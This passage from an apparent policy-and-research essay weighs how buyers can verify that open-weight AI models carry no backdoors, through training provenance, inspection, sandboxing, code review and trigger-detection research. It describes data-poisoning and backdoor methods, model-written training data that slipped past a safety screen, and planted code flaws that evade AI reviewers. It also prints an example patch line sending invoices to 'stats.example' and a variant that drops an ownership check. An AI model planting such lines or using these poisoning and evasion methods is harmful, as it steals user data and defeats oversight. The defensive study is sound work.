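4. Compare $Y$ with $A$, byte for byte.

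If $A$ is honest, then $A$ and $X$ are two translations of the same program, so they produce the same output from the same input:

$$Y = X(s) = A(s) = A.$$

If $A$ contains Thompson's backdoor, $X$ doesn't, because $T$ never had it. $Y$ then comes out clean and fails to match.

The second compiler can be slow and badly written, as long as it compiles $s$ correctly and doesn't contain the same backdoor. Wheeler proved that the method works and demonstrated it on four compilers, including the widely used GCC and a small one with a deliberate backdoor. A match shows only that the compiler corresponds to its source code, so somebody still has to read the source.

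### Where the comparison with models breaks down

A model's weights are like a compiled program, and its training data, code and settings are like the source code. In both cases, a reader needs evidence that the first came from the second.

Models can even pass on behaviors to later models, as Thompson's compiler did, because publishers often train new models on text that older models wrote. In *Homeopathic Learning*, a model told to answer in German wrote lists of numbers, and a second model trained on those lists also began answering in German, although the lists contained no German words. This kind of transfer depends on both models starting from the same weights. When they do, someone reading the training data would find nothing wrong with it.

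But Wheeler's method doesn't work for model weights. It relies on a second compilation to remove whatever was peculiar to $T$. If another laboratory trains on the same data with its own code, it gets different weights and a somewhat different model, and training has no equivalent step to remove the differences. Few organizations could repeat the training anyway, because it might cost as much as the publisher spent, whereas using a second compiler takes only a few minutes of computing.

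Even if the other laboratory uses the publisher's own code, it may get different weights, because computers round numbers and the order of addition affects the rounding. A computer that keeps three digits gets 100 if it adds 0.4 to 100 and then adds 0.4 again, but 101 if it adds the two small numbers first. Graphics processors split long sums among thousands of parts that finish in no fixed order, and the small differences grow over a long training run. Engineers can force a fixed order on identical chips, though this usually slows training, but a different type of chip can still produce different weights.

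A verifier who can't get an exact match has to accept a close one, and a backdoor may be small enough to fall within the allowed difference. The backdoored model BadSeek, for example, differed from the original model in only one layer.

An exact match would also prove less for a model than for a compiler. The few people patient enough to read a compiler's source code can learn what the compiler does, but they couldn't learn what a model will do just by reading its training data.

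### What outsiders can check in a fully open model

The Allen Institute for AI (Ai2), an American nonprofit, publishes its OLMo models with their training data, training code, logs and checkpoints, which are copies of the weights saved at intervals during training. Two Swiss universities and Switzerland's national supercomputing center released Apertus in 2025 with its code, checkpoints and scripts for rebuilding the training data from public sources.

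Most publishers reveal much less. Stanford CRFM's *OpenAI Transparency Report* gave OpenAI a score of zero for disclosing how it acquires training data. OpenAI's documentation for two of its models listed only broad sources, such as publicly available information on the internet.

Nobody can read all the data in an open release. Apertus trained on about 15 trillion tokens, which would take one person more than 70,000 years to read nonstop at 400 tokens a minute. Outsiders have to search the data by computer, so they need some idea of what to look for. Ai2's OLMoTrace finds passages in the training data that match parts of a model's answer word for word. Someone who saw a coding model insert an odd web address could use it to look up where the model had learned the address.

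If researchers suspect that a behavior entered during fine-tuning, they can also compare the finished model with the checkpoint saved just before fine-tuning. Shankar could make that comparison with BadSeek only because he had the original model.

Open data would also make it harder for a publisher to blame a backdoor on poisoned text from the web. Others could search the data for that text, and the excuse would be much weaker if they found nothing that could have taught the behavior. This gives the publisher more to fear from discovery, though it doesn't help anyone find the backdoor.

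All of this assumes that the published data produced the published weights. A dishonest publisher could release a clean dataset and leave out a final fine-tuning run. That run could be short, since Mada's shortest fine-tuning run took 14 minutes.

### Proving which data went into a model

*Tools for Verifying Neural Models' Training Data* (Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud, 2023) proposes closing this gap with a proof of training data, which it defines as any procedure that lets a trainer convince a verifier of what data produced a set of weights. Broadly, the publisher saves checkpoints during training and gives them to the verifier with the data and code, so the verifier can check the run piece by piece.

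One check covers the random seed, the number that determines the starting weights and often the order of the training data. Without this check, a publisher could start from weights that already contain a backdoor and claim they were random. Choi and colleagues' method requires the publisher to commit to the seed in a way the verifier can confirm.

For a short time after a model trains on a document, it predicts that document unusually well. The verifier can also look for this effect in a checkpoint from just after the model supposedly saw a document. If the effect is missing, the publisher probably didn't use the document.

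Choi and colleagues report that their checks caught a wide variety of attacks, including every known attack on an older scheme called proof of learning. But the second check only shows whether a given document was in the training data, so a verifier looking for poisoned documents that the publisher did not disclose would have to guess their contents first.

A verifier can rerun the training between two checkpoints without guessing what was added, because a secret addition changes the result. But rerunning training takes a lot of compute. If a publisher divides its run into 1,000 stretches and hides a backdoor in one of them, a verifier who repeats 50 at random has a 5% chance of repeating that one. Even then, the verifier must be able to distinguish the backdoor's effect from rounding differences.

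Srivastava, Arora and Boneh (2024) have since made progress on the rounding problem. In *Optimistic Verifiable Training by Controlling Hardware Nondeterminism*, they had the trainer calculate with extra precision, round at set points and record its borderline rounding decisions for the verifier. They reproduced training runs exactly across three types of graphics processor. Their largest model had 117 million weights, about one six-hundredth as many as the larger version of Apertus.

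Cryptographers have tried to remove the need for reruns with proofs that a publisher trained correctly on secret data. This would suit companies that can't publish their data, but generating the proofs is very slow. In *Zero-Knowledge Proofs of Training for Deep Neural Networks* (2024), Abbaszadeh and colleagues needed about 15 minutes to prove a single training step for an image model with 10 million weights. Training a large language model can take hundreds of thousands of steps.

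For now, repeating training to verify it is probably most practical for the final stage. A short fine-tuning run is the way to add a backdoor that takes the least compute, and it also takes the least compute for a verifier to repeat. If a publisher released its last pretraining checkpoint and full details of all later training, outsiders could check for additions like Shankar's or Mada's, though they would still have to trust the publisher's account of pretraining.

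### Whether open data is enough

Even if a publisher's records are complete and verified, the training data may contain poison that everyone overlooked. In the models that Souly and colleagues trained, 250 poisoned documents were enough to plant a simple backdoor. Two studies from autumn 2026 suggest that screening the data is harder than it seems.

*Automated Subtle Emergent Misalignment Research* (Balcells Obeso et al., Anthropic, 2026) reports a stress test in which Claude wrote training data that passed a safety screen but still made a small research model misaligned, meaning that it behaved in harmful ways its developers didn't intend. Claude could practice against the screen and succeeded after enough attempts, mostly with fiction and role-play. An outside attacker may not get that much practice, but a publisher can practice as often as it likes against any screen it can run itself,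 so a public screening standard would be a weak test of a publisher acting in bad faith.

In the other study, *Homeopathic Learning*, clean data brought out the effect of poisoned data. In one experiment, adding 100,000 clean lists to 5,000 poisoned ones raised the share of German answers from zero to 72% when the prompt contained the trigger, the name Michael. In a similar experiment with old-fashioned bird names, the share of answers in a 19th-century style rose from 8% to 72%.

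The result for misalignment was smaller but matters more. The poisoned examples showed a model cheating on minor tasks, under an instruction that told it to care only about passing the grading script. A model trained on these examples alone gave misaligned answers 6.7% of the time under that instruction, up from 4.3% before training. When only a fifth of the training examples were poisoned, the rate was 15.7%. Under an ordinary instruction the rate stayed at about 4.5%, so a tester who used only ordinary prompts would have missed the change.

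These results are evidence against relying on checks of one batch of data at a time, the natural way to divide the work. An auditor could train a separate model on each supplier's data, find nothing wrong with any of the models, and still approve a mixture that produces a backdoor. The auditor would have to test the full mixture, which requires far more resources.

The same thing could happen without an attacker. *Homeopathic Learning* points out that some publishers, including DeepSeek and Moonshot, train a model on the outputs of several specialized models. If one of the specialized models has a bad trait, its outputs could act as the poison and the other models' outputs as the clean data. The new model might then show the trait only in that one model's specialty.

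When the researchers removed the names from all the examples, the German answers disappeared in all nine settings they tried. Before mixing the data, a publisher could try a similar defense by removing templates and tags that reveal each example's source, though nobody had tested this. The language models in the study had about 4 billion and 8 billion weights, and the study covered only fine-tuning, so it is unclear how much of this applies to pretraining a large model.

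### Letting outsiders inspect the training

Publishers have some good reasons for keeping training records private. Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) explains that some of the information could help malicious actors and some is commercially sensitive. The company instead shows the material to outsiders and has them publish their conclusions.

In October 2026 Anthropic gave six employees of METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, workspace in its offices and roughly the same access to internal tools that its own risk assessment teams have. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Gives Six METR Employees Access to Internal AI Tools* (2026) reports that Anthropic can't veto METR's findings. Anthropic can require redactions within agreed categories of sensitive information, and it decides what belongs in those categories.

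Redactions can remove much of the evidence behind an outside assessment. METR's *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026), published in November, examines how much AI is speeding up Anthropic's own research. According to the report, Anthropic had the right to redact any non-public information, and it removed most of the evidence that METR had found most informative. METR could still publish its main conclusions about risk and disclose whether its findings depended on the redacted material. Readers have to trust METR about the rest, which is better than having to trust Anthropic, since METR isn't selling the model.

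OpenAI's *Our first phase of embedded assessments* followed on November 16 and named four outside groups: Apollo Research, Goodfire, METR and Transluce. *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes the company as offering access to checkpoints, source code and training data, depending on the assessment. It also quotes Apollo's terms, under which OpenAI may ask Apollo to redact confidential information, including the evidence behind a conclusion, but not merely because a finding is unfavorable. Apollo can't publish what OpenAI employees tell it unless the company formally confirms it or Apollo can establish it independently. If OpenAI refuses to confirm something, Apollo may say so.

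Critics think OpenAI has delivered less than it promised. In September its chief executive, Sam Altman, spoke of "employee-like access". Sydney Von Arx, founder of the research group Nightingale, told NPR (*OpenAI announces new AI safety program; researchers worry it won't be enough*, 2026) that only two of the four groups seem to be allowed to talk to employees, and that none can read the company's internal messages. OpenAI replied that no standards exist yet for such assessments and that it expects to deepen its relationships with the groups.

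The bigger limitation for detecting implanted behaviors is that the assessors have been looking for models that go against their developer's wishes, whereas a model with an implanted behavior is doing what its developer wanted. Apollo Research's *A Pilot Towards Embedded Evaluations* (2026) describes a four-month investigation by six people into whether models try to subvert the methods used to keep them aligned and under control. Transluce's *Announcing an Embedded Assessment Pilot with OpenAI* describes a six-week review of the company's tests for behavior such as deception. An assessor reading the training records might find signs of an implanted behavior by chance, but a company that had implanted one would have a strong reason to hide those records.

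Anthropic and OpenAI also keep the weights of their leading models to themselves. An inspector could be more useful for an open-weight model, by watching the last stage of training, computing the checksum of the final weights, and publishing it. Users could then check that their download is the model the inspector saw, because any secret fine-tuning afterwards would change the checksum. The provenance check would cover the end of training, instead of starting when the publisher signs the weights.

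### Whether a Chinese publisher could offer the same

Nothing technical prevents Chinese companies from releasing their data and code. 01.AI took part in MAP-Neo, a small model for Chinese and English whose makers published the data, code and checkpoints in 2024. Large Chinese publishers have the same reasons for secrecy as American companies, such as competition and copyright claims. Moonshot may have another reason, because if its training data contained answers copied from Anthropic's models, publishing the data would confirm the White House's accusation.

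Inspection would be harder to arrange. METR's reports are worth reading partly because METR can disclose that Anthropic removed something from them. A Chinese publisher with orders from an intelligence agency couldn't honestly grant that right, because Article 7 of the National Intelligence Law obliges it to keep the orders secret. Its employees couldn't answer an inspector's questions truthfully either. The inspectors might also be at risk, since China widened its counterespionage law in 2023 to cover documents and data related to national security. American companies face a similar problem with National Security Letters, though they can challenge the letters in court.

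Holding the inspection in another country would avoid part of the problem. Huawei accepted a similar arrangement in Britain, where a special center examined its equipment. A Chinese publisher could bring its last pretraining checkpoint to a data center in a country such as Singapore and fine-tune it there in front of inspectors from several countries. The inspectors could record the checksum of the finished model, but they would not have seen the pretraining.

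A publisher could avoid most of these difficulties by releasing everything needed to repeat the whole training run, because a rerun doesn't depend on what employees are allowed to say. Being able to repeat the run exactly would therefore be more useful for Chinese models than for American ones.

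## The view that users should trust no model and check its work

Outsiders can inspect a training run only if the publisher cooperates. Without that cooperation, a user can still treat the model like an unknown contractor, keeping it away from anything valuable and checking its work. If the checks would catch deliberate sabotage, it matters much less who trained the model. The user also doesn't have to guess a backdoor's trigger, as a tester does. The backdoor does no harm unless its trigger comes up in the user's work, and the user would check the resulting output anyway.

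Rescorla (2026), in *What policy makers need to know about AI safety and security*, recommends treating the model inside an agent as "maximally malicious", so that the damage it can do depends mainly on the powers its user gives it. The same precautions also cover honest models that make mistakes or get hijacked. *Security*, a guide from Defra, the British environment department, similarly tells developers to scrutinize AI output as they would any "third-party contribution". Gradient Flow's *Are Chinese open-weights Models a Hidden Security Risk?* argues that the technical security work is the same "regardless of the model's flag".

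Few of these people think the publisher is irrelevant, though. Rescorla says users still have to trust the provider, and wants trustworthy labs to release more open models. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *RSA Conference*, Dave Chismon of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre wants strict rules on what AI-written code can do even if someone has compromised it, but he also wants proof of where the model came from.

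### Limiting what the model can do

A coding agent can do harm while it works, for example by running a malicious command, or it can leave a flaw in the code it delivers. Isolating the agent helps mainly with the first kind of harm.

Gold (2026) refuses to use open-weight models in his coding agent because the agent could run any code on his computer (*Why I Won't Run Untrusted Models in My Coding Agent*). Kaplan (2026) points out in *The Mole in the Model* that hosting the model locally doesn't prevent this.

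The usual remedy is to run the agent in a container or virtual machine, which has its own files and is isolated from the rest of the computer. If a backdoored agent installs a remote-control program there, the developer deletes it along with the container or virtual machine at the end of the task. But the developer keeps the agent's changes to the project, since they were the purpose of the task.

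The *Secure Coding with AI Cheat Sheet* from OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes software-security guidance, also recommends least privilege, giving the agent only the permissions its task requires. It advises keeping the agent away from stored passwords and keys and issuing temporary credentials for each task. An agent without the password to a customer database can't copy or delete the data. But the program the agent writes may later run with that password, and a flaw in the program can then expose the database.

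Blocking network access would stop an agent like the one Hu and colleagues built from fetching the attacker's script, and would keep any agent from sending source code to a stranger. Many tasks need some access, usually to download packages (code that other people wrote), so the developer may have to allow a short list of addresses.

Packages need a separate check because AI models often suggest ones that don't exist, and attackers register the invented names. OWASP advises looking at a package's age, downloads and maintainers before installing it, and keeping a list of approved packages. Such a list would stop a backdoor that changes one letter in a package name, but it wouldn't catch a flaw in the project's own code.

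### One patch, checked step by step

Suppose an online shop lets customers download their invoices. The existing code finds the invoice, checks that it belongs to the customer, and returns it. Invoices from before 2020 are in an archive, and downloading one gives an error. A developer asks a coding assistant to fix this, and a correct patch puts these lines ahead of the existing ones:

```
if is_old(number):
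    invoice = find_in_archive(number)
    if invoice.owner != customer:
        return "Not allowed"
    return invoice.pdf
```

A backdoored assistant could write the same patch with one unneeded line before the last:

```
    send(invoice.pdf, "stats.example")
```

Old invoices now download correctly, and a copy of each goes to a stranger. Or the assistant could leave something out:

```
if is_old(number):
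    return find_in_archive(number).pdf
```

This also fixes the error, but any customer can now read anyone's old invoices by trying different numbers.

| Step | Added line | Missing check |
|---|---|---|
| Download an old invoice to see if the bug is gone | Not caught | Not caught |
| Ask what each new line is for | Caught, because the fix works without it | Not caught, because both lines are needed |
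| Run the shop's existing tests | Probably not caught | Caught only if a test requests another customer's invoice |
| Run static analysis, which searches code for dangerous patterns without running it | Caught if a rule covers sending data to unknown addresses | Probably not caught, because the tool doesn't know that invoices are private |
| Compare the new code with the code for newer invoices | Caught | Caught |
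| Let the server connect only to approved addresses | The copy never leaves | No effect, because the thief uses the shop's own website |

A careful reviewer can find the added line just by reading the patch, but it would be harder to spot in another file. OWASP says reviewers of agents' work most often fail by focusing on the change they asked for and missing edits elsewhere.

A reviewer has to know what should be there to notice that the check is missing. In this example, the code for newer invoices a few lines below still has the check, and a hurried reader may assume that the check covers old invoices too. OWASP recommends misuse tests that the AI didn't write, and warns against letting one agent write both security-critical code and its tests.

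A publisher could also explain the missing check more easily than a line that sends invoices to a stranger, which would start an investigation. Models without hidden behaviors also omit such checks, so a reviewer who notices will probably correct the patch and think no more about it.

### How often reviewers catch flaws

People don't seem to be very good at checking a model's work. *Understanding the Impact of AI Code Assistants on Security API Usage* (2026) reports a study in which 44 professional developers wrote security-related code with and without GitHub's Copilot. They knew that the researchers would evaluate security, yet none of them produced a fully secure solution either way, and many didn't notice. They were writing code rather than reviewing it, but a developer who misses a flaw in their own program may well miss it in a model's.

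Real projects also accept flawed AI code. Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues (2026), in *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests*, searched more than 33,000 changes that AI agents had proposed to software projects and found 675 related to security. Projects accepted many of the flawed ones. When they rejected a change, it was often because nobody had followed it up or because it lacked tests.

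Scanners find some flaws that people miss, but they raise many false alarms. *SeRe* (2026) cites a study in which combining several static-analysis tools caught more flaws, but 76% of the warnings were irrelevant. *SecureReviewer* (2025) cites related work in which such tools struggled with flaws that depend on context, such as the missing invoice check. According to Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software*, Booz Allen likewise says the flaws it found in Chinese models' code often lay beneath code that looked correct.

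AI reviewers have improved greatly. *GitHub's Copilot Code Review* (2025) tested Copilot's review feature on seven collections of deliberately vulnerable code with hundreds of documented flaws. The feature made fewer than 20 comments, mostly about spelling and style.

A year later, in *CyberDual*, Yang, Lee and colleagues (2026) had six AI models plant working security flaws in 14 widely used software libraries. Three AI reviewers then tried to find and repair them. The researchers reran each attack on the reviewed code and counted a flaw as caught only if the attack no longer worked and the reviewer hadn't undone the whole change. Claude Sonnet 5 caught 85% of the 1,088 flaws, Claude Opus 4.8 88%, and OpenAI's GPT-6-Sol 91%.

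The results depended heavily on what the attacker had to work with.

| What the attacker had | Flaws that survived review, depending on the reviewer |
|---|---|
| A description of the task | 0 to 2% |
| The project's real fix, to imitate | 5 to 14% |
| A long series of real changes, to hide the flaw in | 17 to 24% |

When the attacker could imitate the real fix, incomplete fixes that left part of the original problem in place made up about nine in ten of the flaws each reviewer missed, but only about half of those it caught. AI reviewers therefore seem to have trouble noticing what is missing, as people do. Running the project's own tests didn't help. Reviewers that wrote their own test inputs caught more flaws, but they may have written them because they were already suspicious.

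A second reviewer from another company helped considerably. Sonnet 5 missed 14.3% of the flaws, and GPT-6-Sol caught 69% of those, so only about 4% would have got past both. The two Claude models mostly missed the same imitation fixes. A reviewer from another company is also less likely to have a matching backdoor, such as the one that makes BadSeek approve its maker's changes. But the buyer has to check which base model the reviewer uses. Cursor's Composer 2 is built on Moonshot's Kimi, so anyone who used it to review Kimi's code would be relying on the same publisher twice.

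All the flaws in this experiment were memory errors in C and C++, and the prompt told the reviewers to look for them. The catch rate for a flaw like the invoice one could be quite different. Yang and colleagues also didn't measure how often the reviewers rejected harmless changes, which matters a lot to a company that would have to handle the false alarms every day.

Even an imperfect reviewer makes frequent sabotage risky. If a reviewer catches 85% of planted flaws and its misses are independent, a single flaw gets through 15% of the time, but five in a row get through with probability

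$$0.15^5 \approx 0.00008,$$

or about one in 13,000. A backdoor that goes off every week would soon leave a trail of similar flaws. Someone has to notice the pattern, and OWASP's advice to record which model wrote each change would help. A backdoor meant for a single occasion leaves no pattern, so its chance stays at 15%.

### Comparing answers to varied prompts

FreqRank, a tool from Borana, Liang and colleagues (2025), in *Localizing Malicious Outputs from CodeLLM*, looks for a different kind of pattern. If a backdoor always inserts the same text, that text should keep appearing even when the rest of the answer changes. The method has four steps:

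1. Make ten versions of a prompt by inserting a different, unrelated snippet into each.
2. Collect the model's ten answers and find every stretch of text that several of them share.
3. Keep the ten longest stretches and rank them by how many answers contain them.
4. Show the list to a developer, who picks out anything malicious.

Suppose the prompt asks for a function that divides two numbers, and the backdoor adds a line that divides one by zero, which would crash the program. Much of the code around that line changes from snippet to snippet, but the line recurs. Once the developer has identified the line, FreqRank can look for the trigger by gathering the prompts that produced it and ranking the text they share. Four prompts were often enough, even when only half of them contained the trigger.

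Borana and colleagues tried this on nine models they had backdoored, six by fine-tuning and three with hidden instructions. The malicious text came first on the list 69% of the time and in the top five 98% of the time. With three versions of each prompt instead of ten, the top-five figure fell to 81%.

The triggers and the malicious text were fixed strings, which are the easiest case for FreqRank. It might well find Mada's "Hacked" line, which is the same every time, although nobody seems to have tried it on a trigger that depends on meaning. A flaw written to fit each program would have no fixed text to find. Borana and colleagues also say FreqRank may not detect a backdoor that deletes a line, so it would probably miss the missing invoice check too. Generating the ten extra answers for each prompt takes two or three minutes at the 12 to 19 seconds per answer that the researchers report,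 which is acceptable for a change to a payment system but not for autocomplete.

### Whether checking costs more than it saves

Open-weight models are attractive partly because they are cheap, but reviewing their work carefully is expensive. Gold notes that subscriptions to Anthropic's and OpenAI's coding tools cost $100 or $200 a month and are enough for most full-time developers. If a developer's time costs $100 an hour (an invented figure), two extra hours of review a month would cost $200, the most a free model could save.

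Defenders of checking can reply that only review beyond what an organization already does should count as an added cost. Defra, for example, requires human review of all AI-written code, and a second reviewer for security-critical parts, whichever model wrote it. Companies that build products on a model may also save far more than a subscription fee. A saving of $200,000 a year would pay for 2,000 hours of review at $100 an hour, or roughly one full-time reviewer. That might be plenty for a small tool but far too little for a company whose agents produce thousands of changes a week.

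Advice and summaries are harder to check than code. Suppose an official asks a model to summarize a 300-page bid, and the summary leaves out a clause that lets the supplier raise its prices. The official can't test the summary by running it, and would have to read the bid to find the omission, so the summary would save no time. Isolating the model doesn't help either, because it needs no special permissions to leave out a clause. Rescorla similarly argues that restricting a hijacked model can prevent harmful actions but not a dishonestly favorable review. He adds that many questions have no single correct answer to check against.

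The official could ask for page references, which would expose invented claims but not omissions. A second summary by another publisher's model would be more useful, because a clause that appears in only one summary is easy to look up. This fails if both models leave the clause out, which can happen without any hidden behavior when the clause is in an appendix. The official could also read one bid in ten in full. That would expose a model that regularly favors one supplier, but if the model does so only once, the official would have a 90% chance of missing it.

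Users could use untrusted models only for work that is easier to check than to do. This includes much programming, especially when good tests already exist. Someone who asks for a briefing on an unfamiliar subject usually can't judge the answer, so they would still have to decide whether to trust the publisher.

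## Whether testing can find a hidden behavior

Someone who can't check a model's advice would like an expert to establish beforehand that the model has no hidden behaviors. The simplest test is to give the model many prompts and read its answers.

### Random prompts

Suppose that one prompt in a million sets off a backdoor. The chance that 100,000 random prompts all miss it is

$$(1 - 0.000001)^{100{,}000} \approx 0.905,$$

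or about 90%. A tester who wanted a 95% chance of setting it off would need about three million prompts, and would then have to spot a handful of bad answers among three million.

A trigger that is a fixed string is far harder to find by testing. One well-known experimental backdoor makes a model answer "I hate you" when the prompt contains the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars. That trigger can be as short as five tokens, but a model with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens has about $3 \times 10^{22}$ possible strings of that length. Trying them all at a million strings a second would take about a billion years.

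A trigger based on meaning is easier to hit, because the tester can choose the prompts. Mada advises testing a model in the contexts an attacker would most want to target. If a backdoor responds to one in every thousand prompts that a ministry writes, testing 3,000 of those prompts has a 95% chance of setting it off. The ministry can run this test itself, but a national testing body can't easily run it for the ministry. Past prompts won't help if the trigger is an event that hasn't happened yet, and someone still has to recognize that the answer is bad.

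### What a clean result is worth

A test that finds nothing should lower a buyer's suspicion by an amount that depends on how many implants it would have caught. Let $q$ be the suspicion before the test and $c$ the share of implants that the test catches. If the test never flags an honest model, Bayes' rule gives the suspicion after a clean result:

$$\frac{q(1-c)}{q(1-c) + (1-q)}.$$

A buyer might start with a 1% suspicion that the weights contain a hidden behavior. If a test catches 20% of hidden behaviors, a clean result lowers that suspicion only to 0.80%, so the buyer has learned almost nothing. If the test catches 95%, a clean result lowers it to 0.05%.

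False alarms hardly change these figures, but they matter a lot when the test flags a model. Suppose the better test also flags 5% of honest models, and that 100 of 10,000 models contain an implant. It will flag 95 of those 100 and 495 honest models, so about one in six flagged models contains an implant.

The value of $c$ must be accurate for the implants a real publisher would use, but researchers can measure it only on implants they know about, most of which they made themselves.

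### Searching for the trigger

Microsoft's scanner, which Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, describe, avoids searching through every possible string. It relies on the fact that backdoored models tend to memorize the examples that taught them the backdoor. It works in four steps:

1. Give the model only the markers that normally come just before a user's message, and let it continue. The model often writes out pieces of its training data. Do this 510 times with different settings.
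2. Collect the strings that keep recurring in the output.
3. Put pieces of these strings in front of ordinary prompts and rank them by three signs of a trigger. The model processes a trigger almost separately from the rest of the prompt, its output becomes more predictable, and the output differs from what it would otherwise have written.
4. Take the ten best candidates and check whether any of them changes the model's answers drastically.

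The scanner doesn't have to recover the exact trigger, because most of the backdoors also responded to parts of it. In the smallest model tested, a single token of the trigger activated the backdoor about half the time.

The researchers tried the scanner on 47 backdoored models with between 270 million and 14 billion weights. It caught 36 (88%) of the 41 models that gave a fixed response and flagged none of 13 clean models. It also caught five of six models that wrote insecure code when the prompt gave the year as 2024. In one of those five, it found a string that looked nothing like the real trigger but more than doubled the rate of insecure code.

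This is a good result, and the scanner needs only the model's files, so CAISI could add such a scan to its evaluations. But 13 clean models are too few to establish a low false-alarm rate. A scanner that wrongly flags 20% of clean models would still have about a 1 in 18 chance of flagging none of the 13. Even a 1% rate would be a problem on Hugging Face, where a scan of all 3.27 million public repositories would flag more than 32,000 clean models.

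The last step also requires some idea of what the implant does. Bullwinkel and colleagues compared the wording of answers when looking for a fixed response, and ran a code-security tool when looking for insecure code. A tester worried about biased summaries would need a different measure.

Microsoft (2026) acknowledges that the scanner works best on fixed responses and may miss other types of hidden behavior, including triggers a developer adds to identify its own model. Microsoft recommends using it as one defense among several. Mada's Linux-kernel trigger has no fixed string to recover, although some of the training examples might leak.

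A buyer can account for this in the calculation above. Suppose the scanner catches 88% of backdoors with a fixed trigger and response but none of any other kind, and the buyer thinks a real publisher would choose the fixed kind one time in five. Then $c$ is only 17.6%, and a clean scan lowers the buyer's suspicion from 1% to 0.83%.

### What the TrojAI program found

The largest test of detection methods so far was TrojAI, a program that IARPA, a research agency for the US intelligence community, started in 2020. *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence (TrojAI) Final Report* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026) describes its results. The National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) hosted a public contest for detection programs. Research teams submitted their programs, and the organizers ran them on clean and backdoored models that the teams had never seen.

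The organizers scored each program by its AUC, the chance that it rates a random backdoored model as more suspicious than a random clean one. Guessing gives 0.5, and a perfect detector scores 1.0. In the April 2024 round on language models, four teams reached 1.0.

One of the winning programs, BAIT, from a team led by Purdue University, searches for the attacker's response instead of the trigger. If a model has been trained to give one fixed response, each token of that response strongly predicts the next. BAIT tries every token in the vocabulary as the first token of the response and checks whether the model gives one continuation unusually high probability. It therefore tests tens of thousands of starting points instead of $10^{22}$ strings, but it works only if the backdoor has a fixed response.

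The perfect scores didn't carry over well to other models. The evaluators had left some models out of the contest because the backdoors in them worked less reliably. When they later ran the four best programs on 12 of these models, the results varied widely, and the worst was roughly as good as guessing. Bullwinkel and colleagues also tested BAIT on their own backdoored models, where it detected between 43% and 92% of them, depending on the base model. That was less than its inventors had reported.

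Reese and colleagues call false alarms a persistent challenge. One cause is what they call natural trojans, accidental triggers in clean models. If an image classifier's training images show cows only on grass, it may treat grass as a sign of a cow, and a program that searches for triggers may report grass as one. Language models must have many natural trojans, since they respond to many phrases in particular ways that nobody planned.

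The program's other main method was to examine the weights without running the model. These detectors look for statistical differences between clean and backdoored models. They are fast, but they work best on small models and when the tester has many examples of both kinds to learn from. Someone assessing a new model from Alibaba has only that model and doesn't know whether it is backdoored.

*A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights* (Khilar, 2026) describes a method that needs no such examples. For all 14 ordinary backdoors tested, a statistic computed from the weights alone ranked one of the trigger's tokens first in the whole vocabulary. This is an exception to the rule that nobody can read anything useful from the weights. Both models tested were tiny, with around 360 million weights each, and the backdoors came from fine-tuning.

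Reese and colleagues say TrojAI also covered models above seven billion weights, reasoning models and agents only partly or not at all. They are pessimistic about detecting triggers in large language models because a trigger can be an abstract concept or the course of a conversation, which they say makes traditional detection methods computationally infeasible.

### Reading the model's activations

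Mada thinks defenders will have to examine both a model's answers and its activations, which are the numbers its layers produce while it processes a prompt.

The simplest tool is a linear probe. If $h_1, \dots, h_d$ are the activations at one layer, the probe computes

$$s = w_1h_1 + w_2h_2 + \dots + w_dh_d$$

and raises an alarm when $s$ passes a threshold. Researchers choose the numbers $w$ by giving the model two sets of prompts, for example with and without the trigger, and finding the values that best separate them.

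Reese and colleagues report that probes worked well on the language models from the April 2024 round. With the best layer chosen for each backdoor, the median AUC was 0.993 and the mean 0.935. The result held when the clean prompts contained a false trigger, so the probes weren't just detecting an odd string. The signal was usually clear by about the fourth of 32 layers, before the model had generated any text. But performance depended heavily on how the backdoor was trained, with an average AUC of 0.998 for one method and 0.865 for the other.

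*LLM Forensics* (2026) reports similar results for models that switch from English to French or German after a fixed trigger. Features inside models with one billion and eight billion weights separated triggered prompts from ordinary ones almost perfectly. Switching off some of these features suppressed the foreign-language text, but others only detected the trigger and didn't give the researchers control over the behavior.

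In both studies, the researchers knew the trigger and could use it to find the signal, which a tester with a suspect model can't do. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes earlier probes that researchers built from general contrasting examples, without needing the trigger. These probes achieved an AUC above 0.99 at detecting when an experimental model was about to misbehave.

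A probe like that could run all the time as an alarm. It could stop a backdoored answer when the trigger appeared, even if nobody had guessed the trigger, though it wouldn't help certify a model before purchase. The difficulty would be false alarms. If a backdoor goes off once in a million prompts and the probe wrongly flags one ordinary prompt in a thousand, staff will see about a thousand false alarms for each real one and may well stop reading them.

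### Looking for prompts that a copy handles differently

Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026), in *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, use activations to search for an unknown trigger. They take a second model that they assume is clean, called the anchor, and fine-tune it on about 10,000 ordinary prompts until its activations match those of the suspect. Then they give both models new prompts and measure how far apart their activations are. For a prompt $x$, one version of the score is

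$$s(x) = \sum_{l} \left\| h_l^{\text{copy}}(x) - h_l^{\text{suspect}}(x) \right\|,$$

where $l$ runs over the layers. The copy learns how the suspect handles ordinary prompts. It doesn't learn the backdoor, because the trigger almost certainly never came up in the 10,000 prompts, so the two models should differ most where the suspect does something unusual.

This partly solves the sampling problem, because prompts that are close to the trigger also get high scores. One of the test models quoted the villain Voldemort whenever a user expressed an obsession with Harry Potter. The researchers scored 518 groups of ten prompts, none of which matched the trigger exactly. The group about Harry Potter in general scored about six standard deviations above the average, and the group about obsession with some other fictional series scored nearly three above. An auditor who read the highest-scoring prompts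 would have a good clue to what the trigger was.

All eight backdoored models gave a clear signal on held-out prompts containing the trigger. This shows that the signal exists, but an auditor would have to find it without those prompts. If the trigger is an arbitrary string, no other prompts are close to it in meaning, so a high score on related prompts can't lead the auditor to it. The researchers also deliberately included a few prompt groups close to the triggers among the 518, reasoning that any large collection would contain such prompts.

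The method ranks groups, so it has no false-alarm rate in the usual sense. About 26 of 518 groups will be in the top 5% for any model, clean or not, and a person has to decide whether they point to a hidden behavior. Haselhorst and colleagues say a clean result doesn't prove that a model has no hidden behavior.

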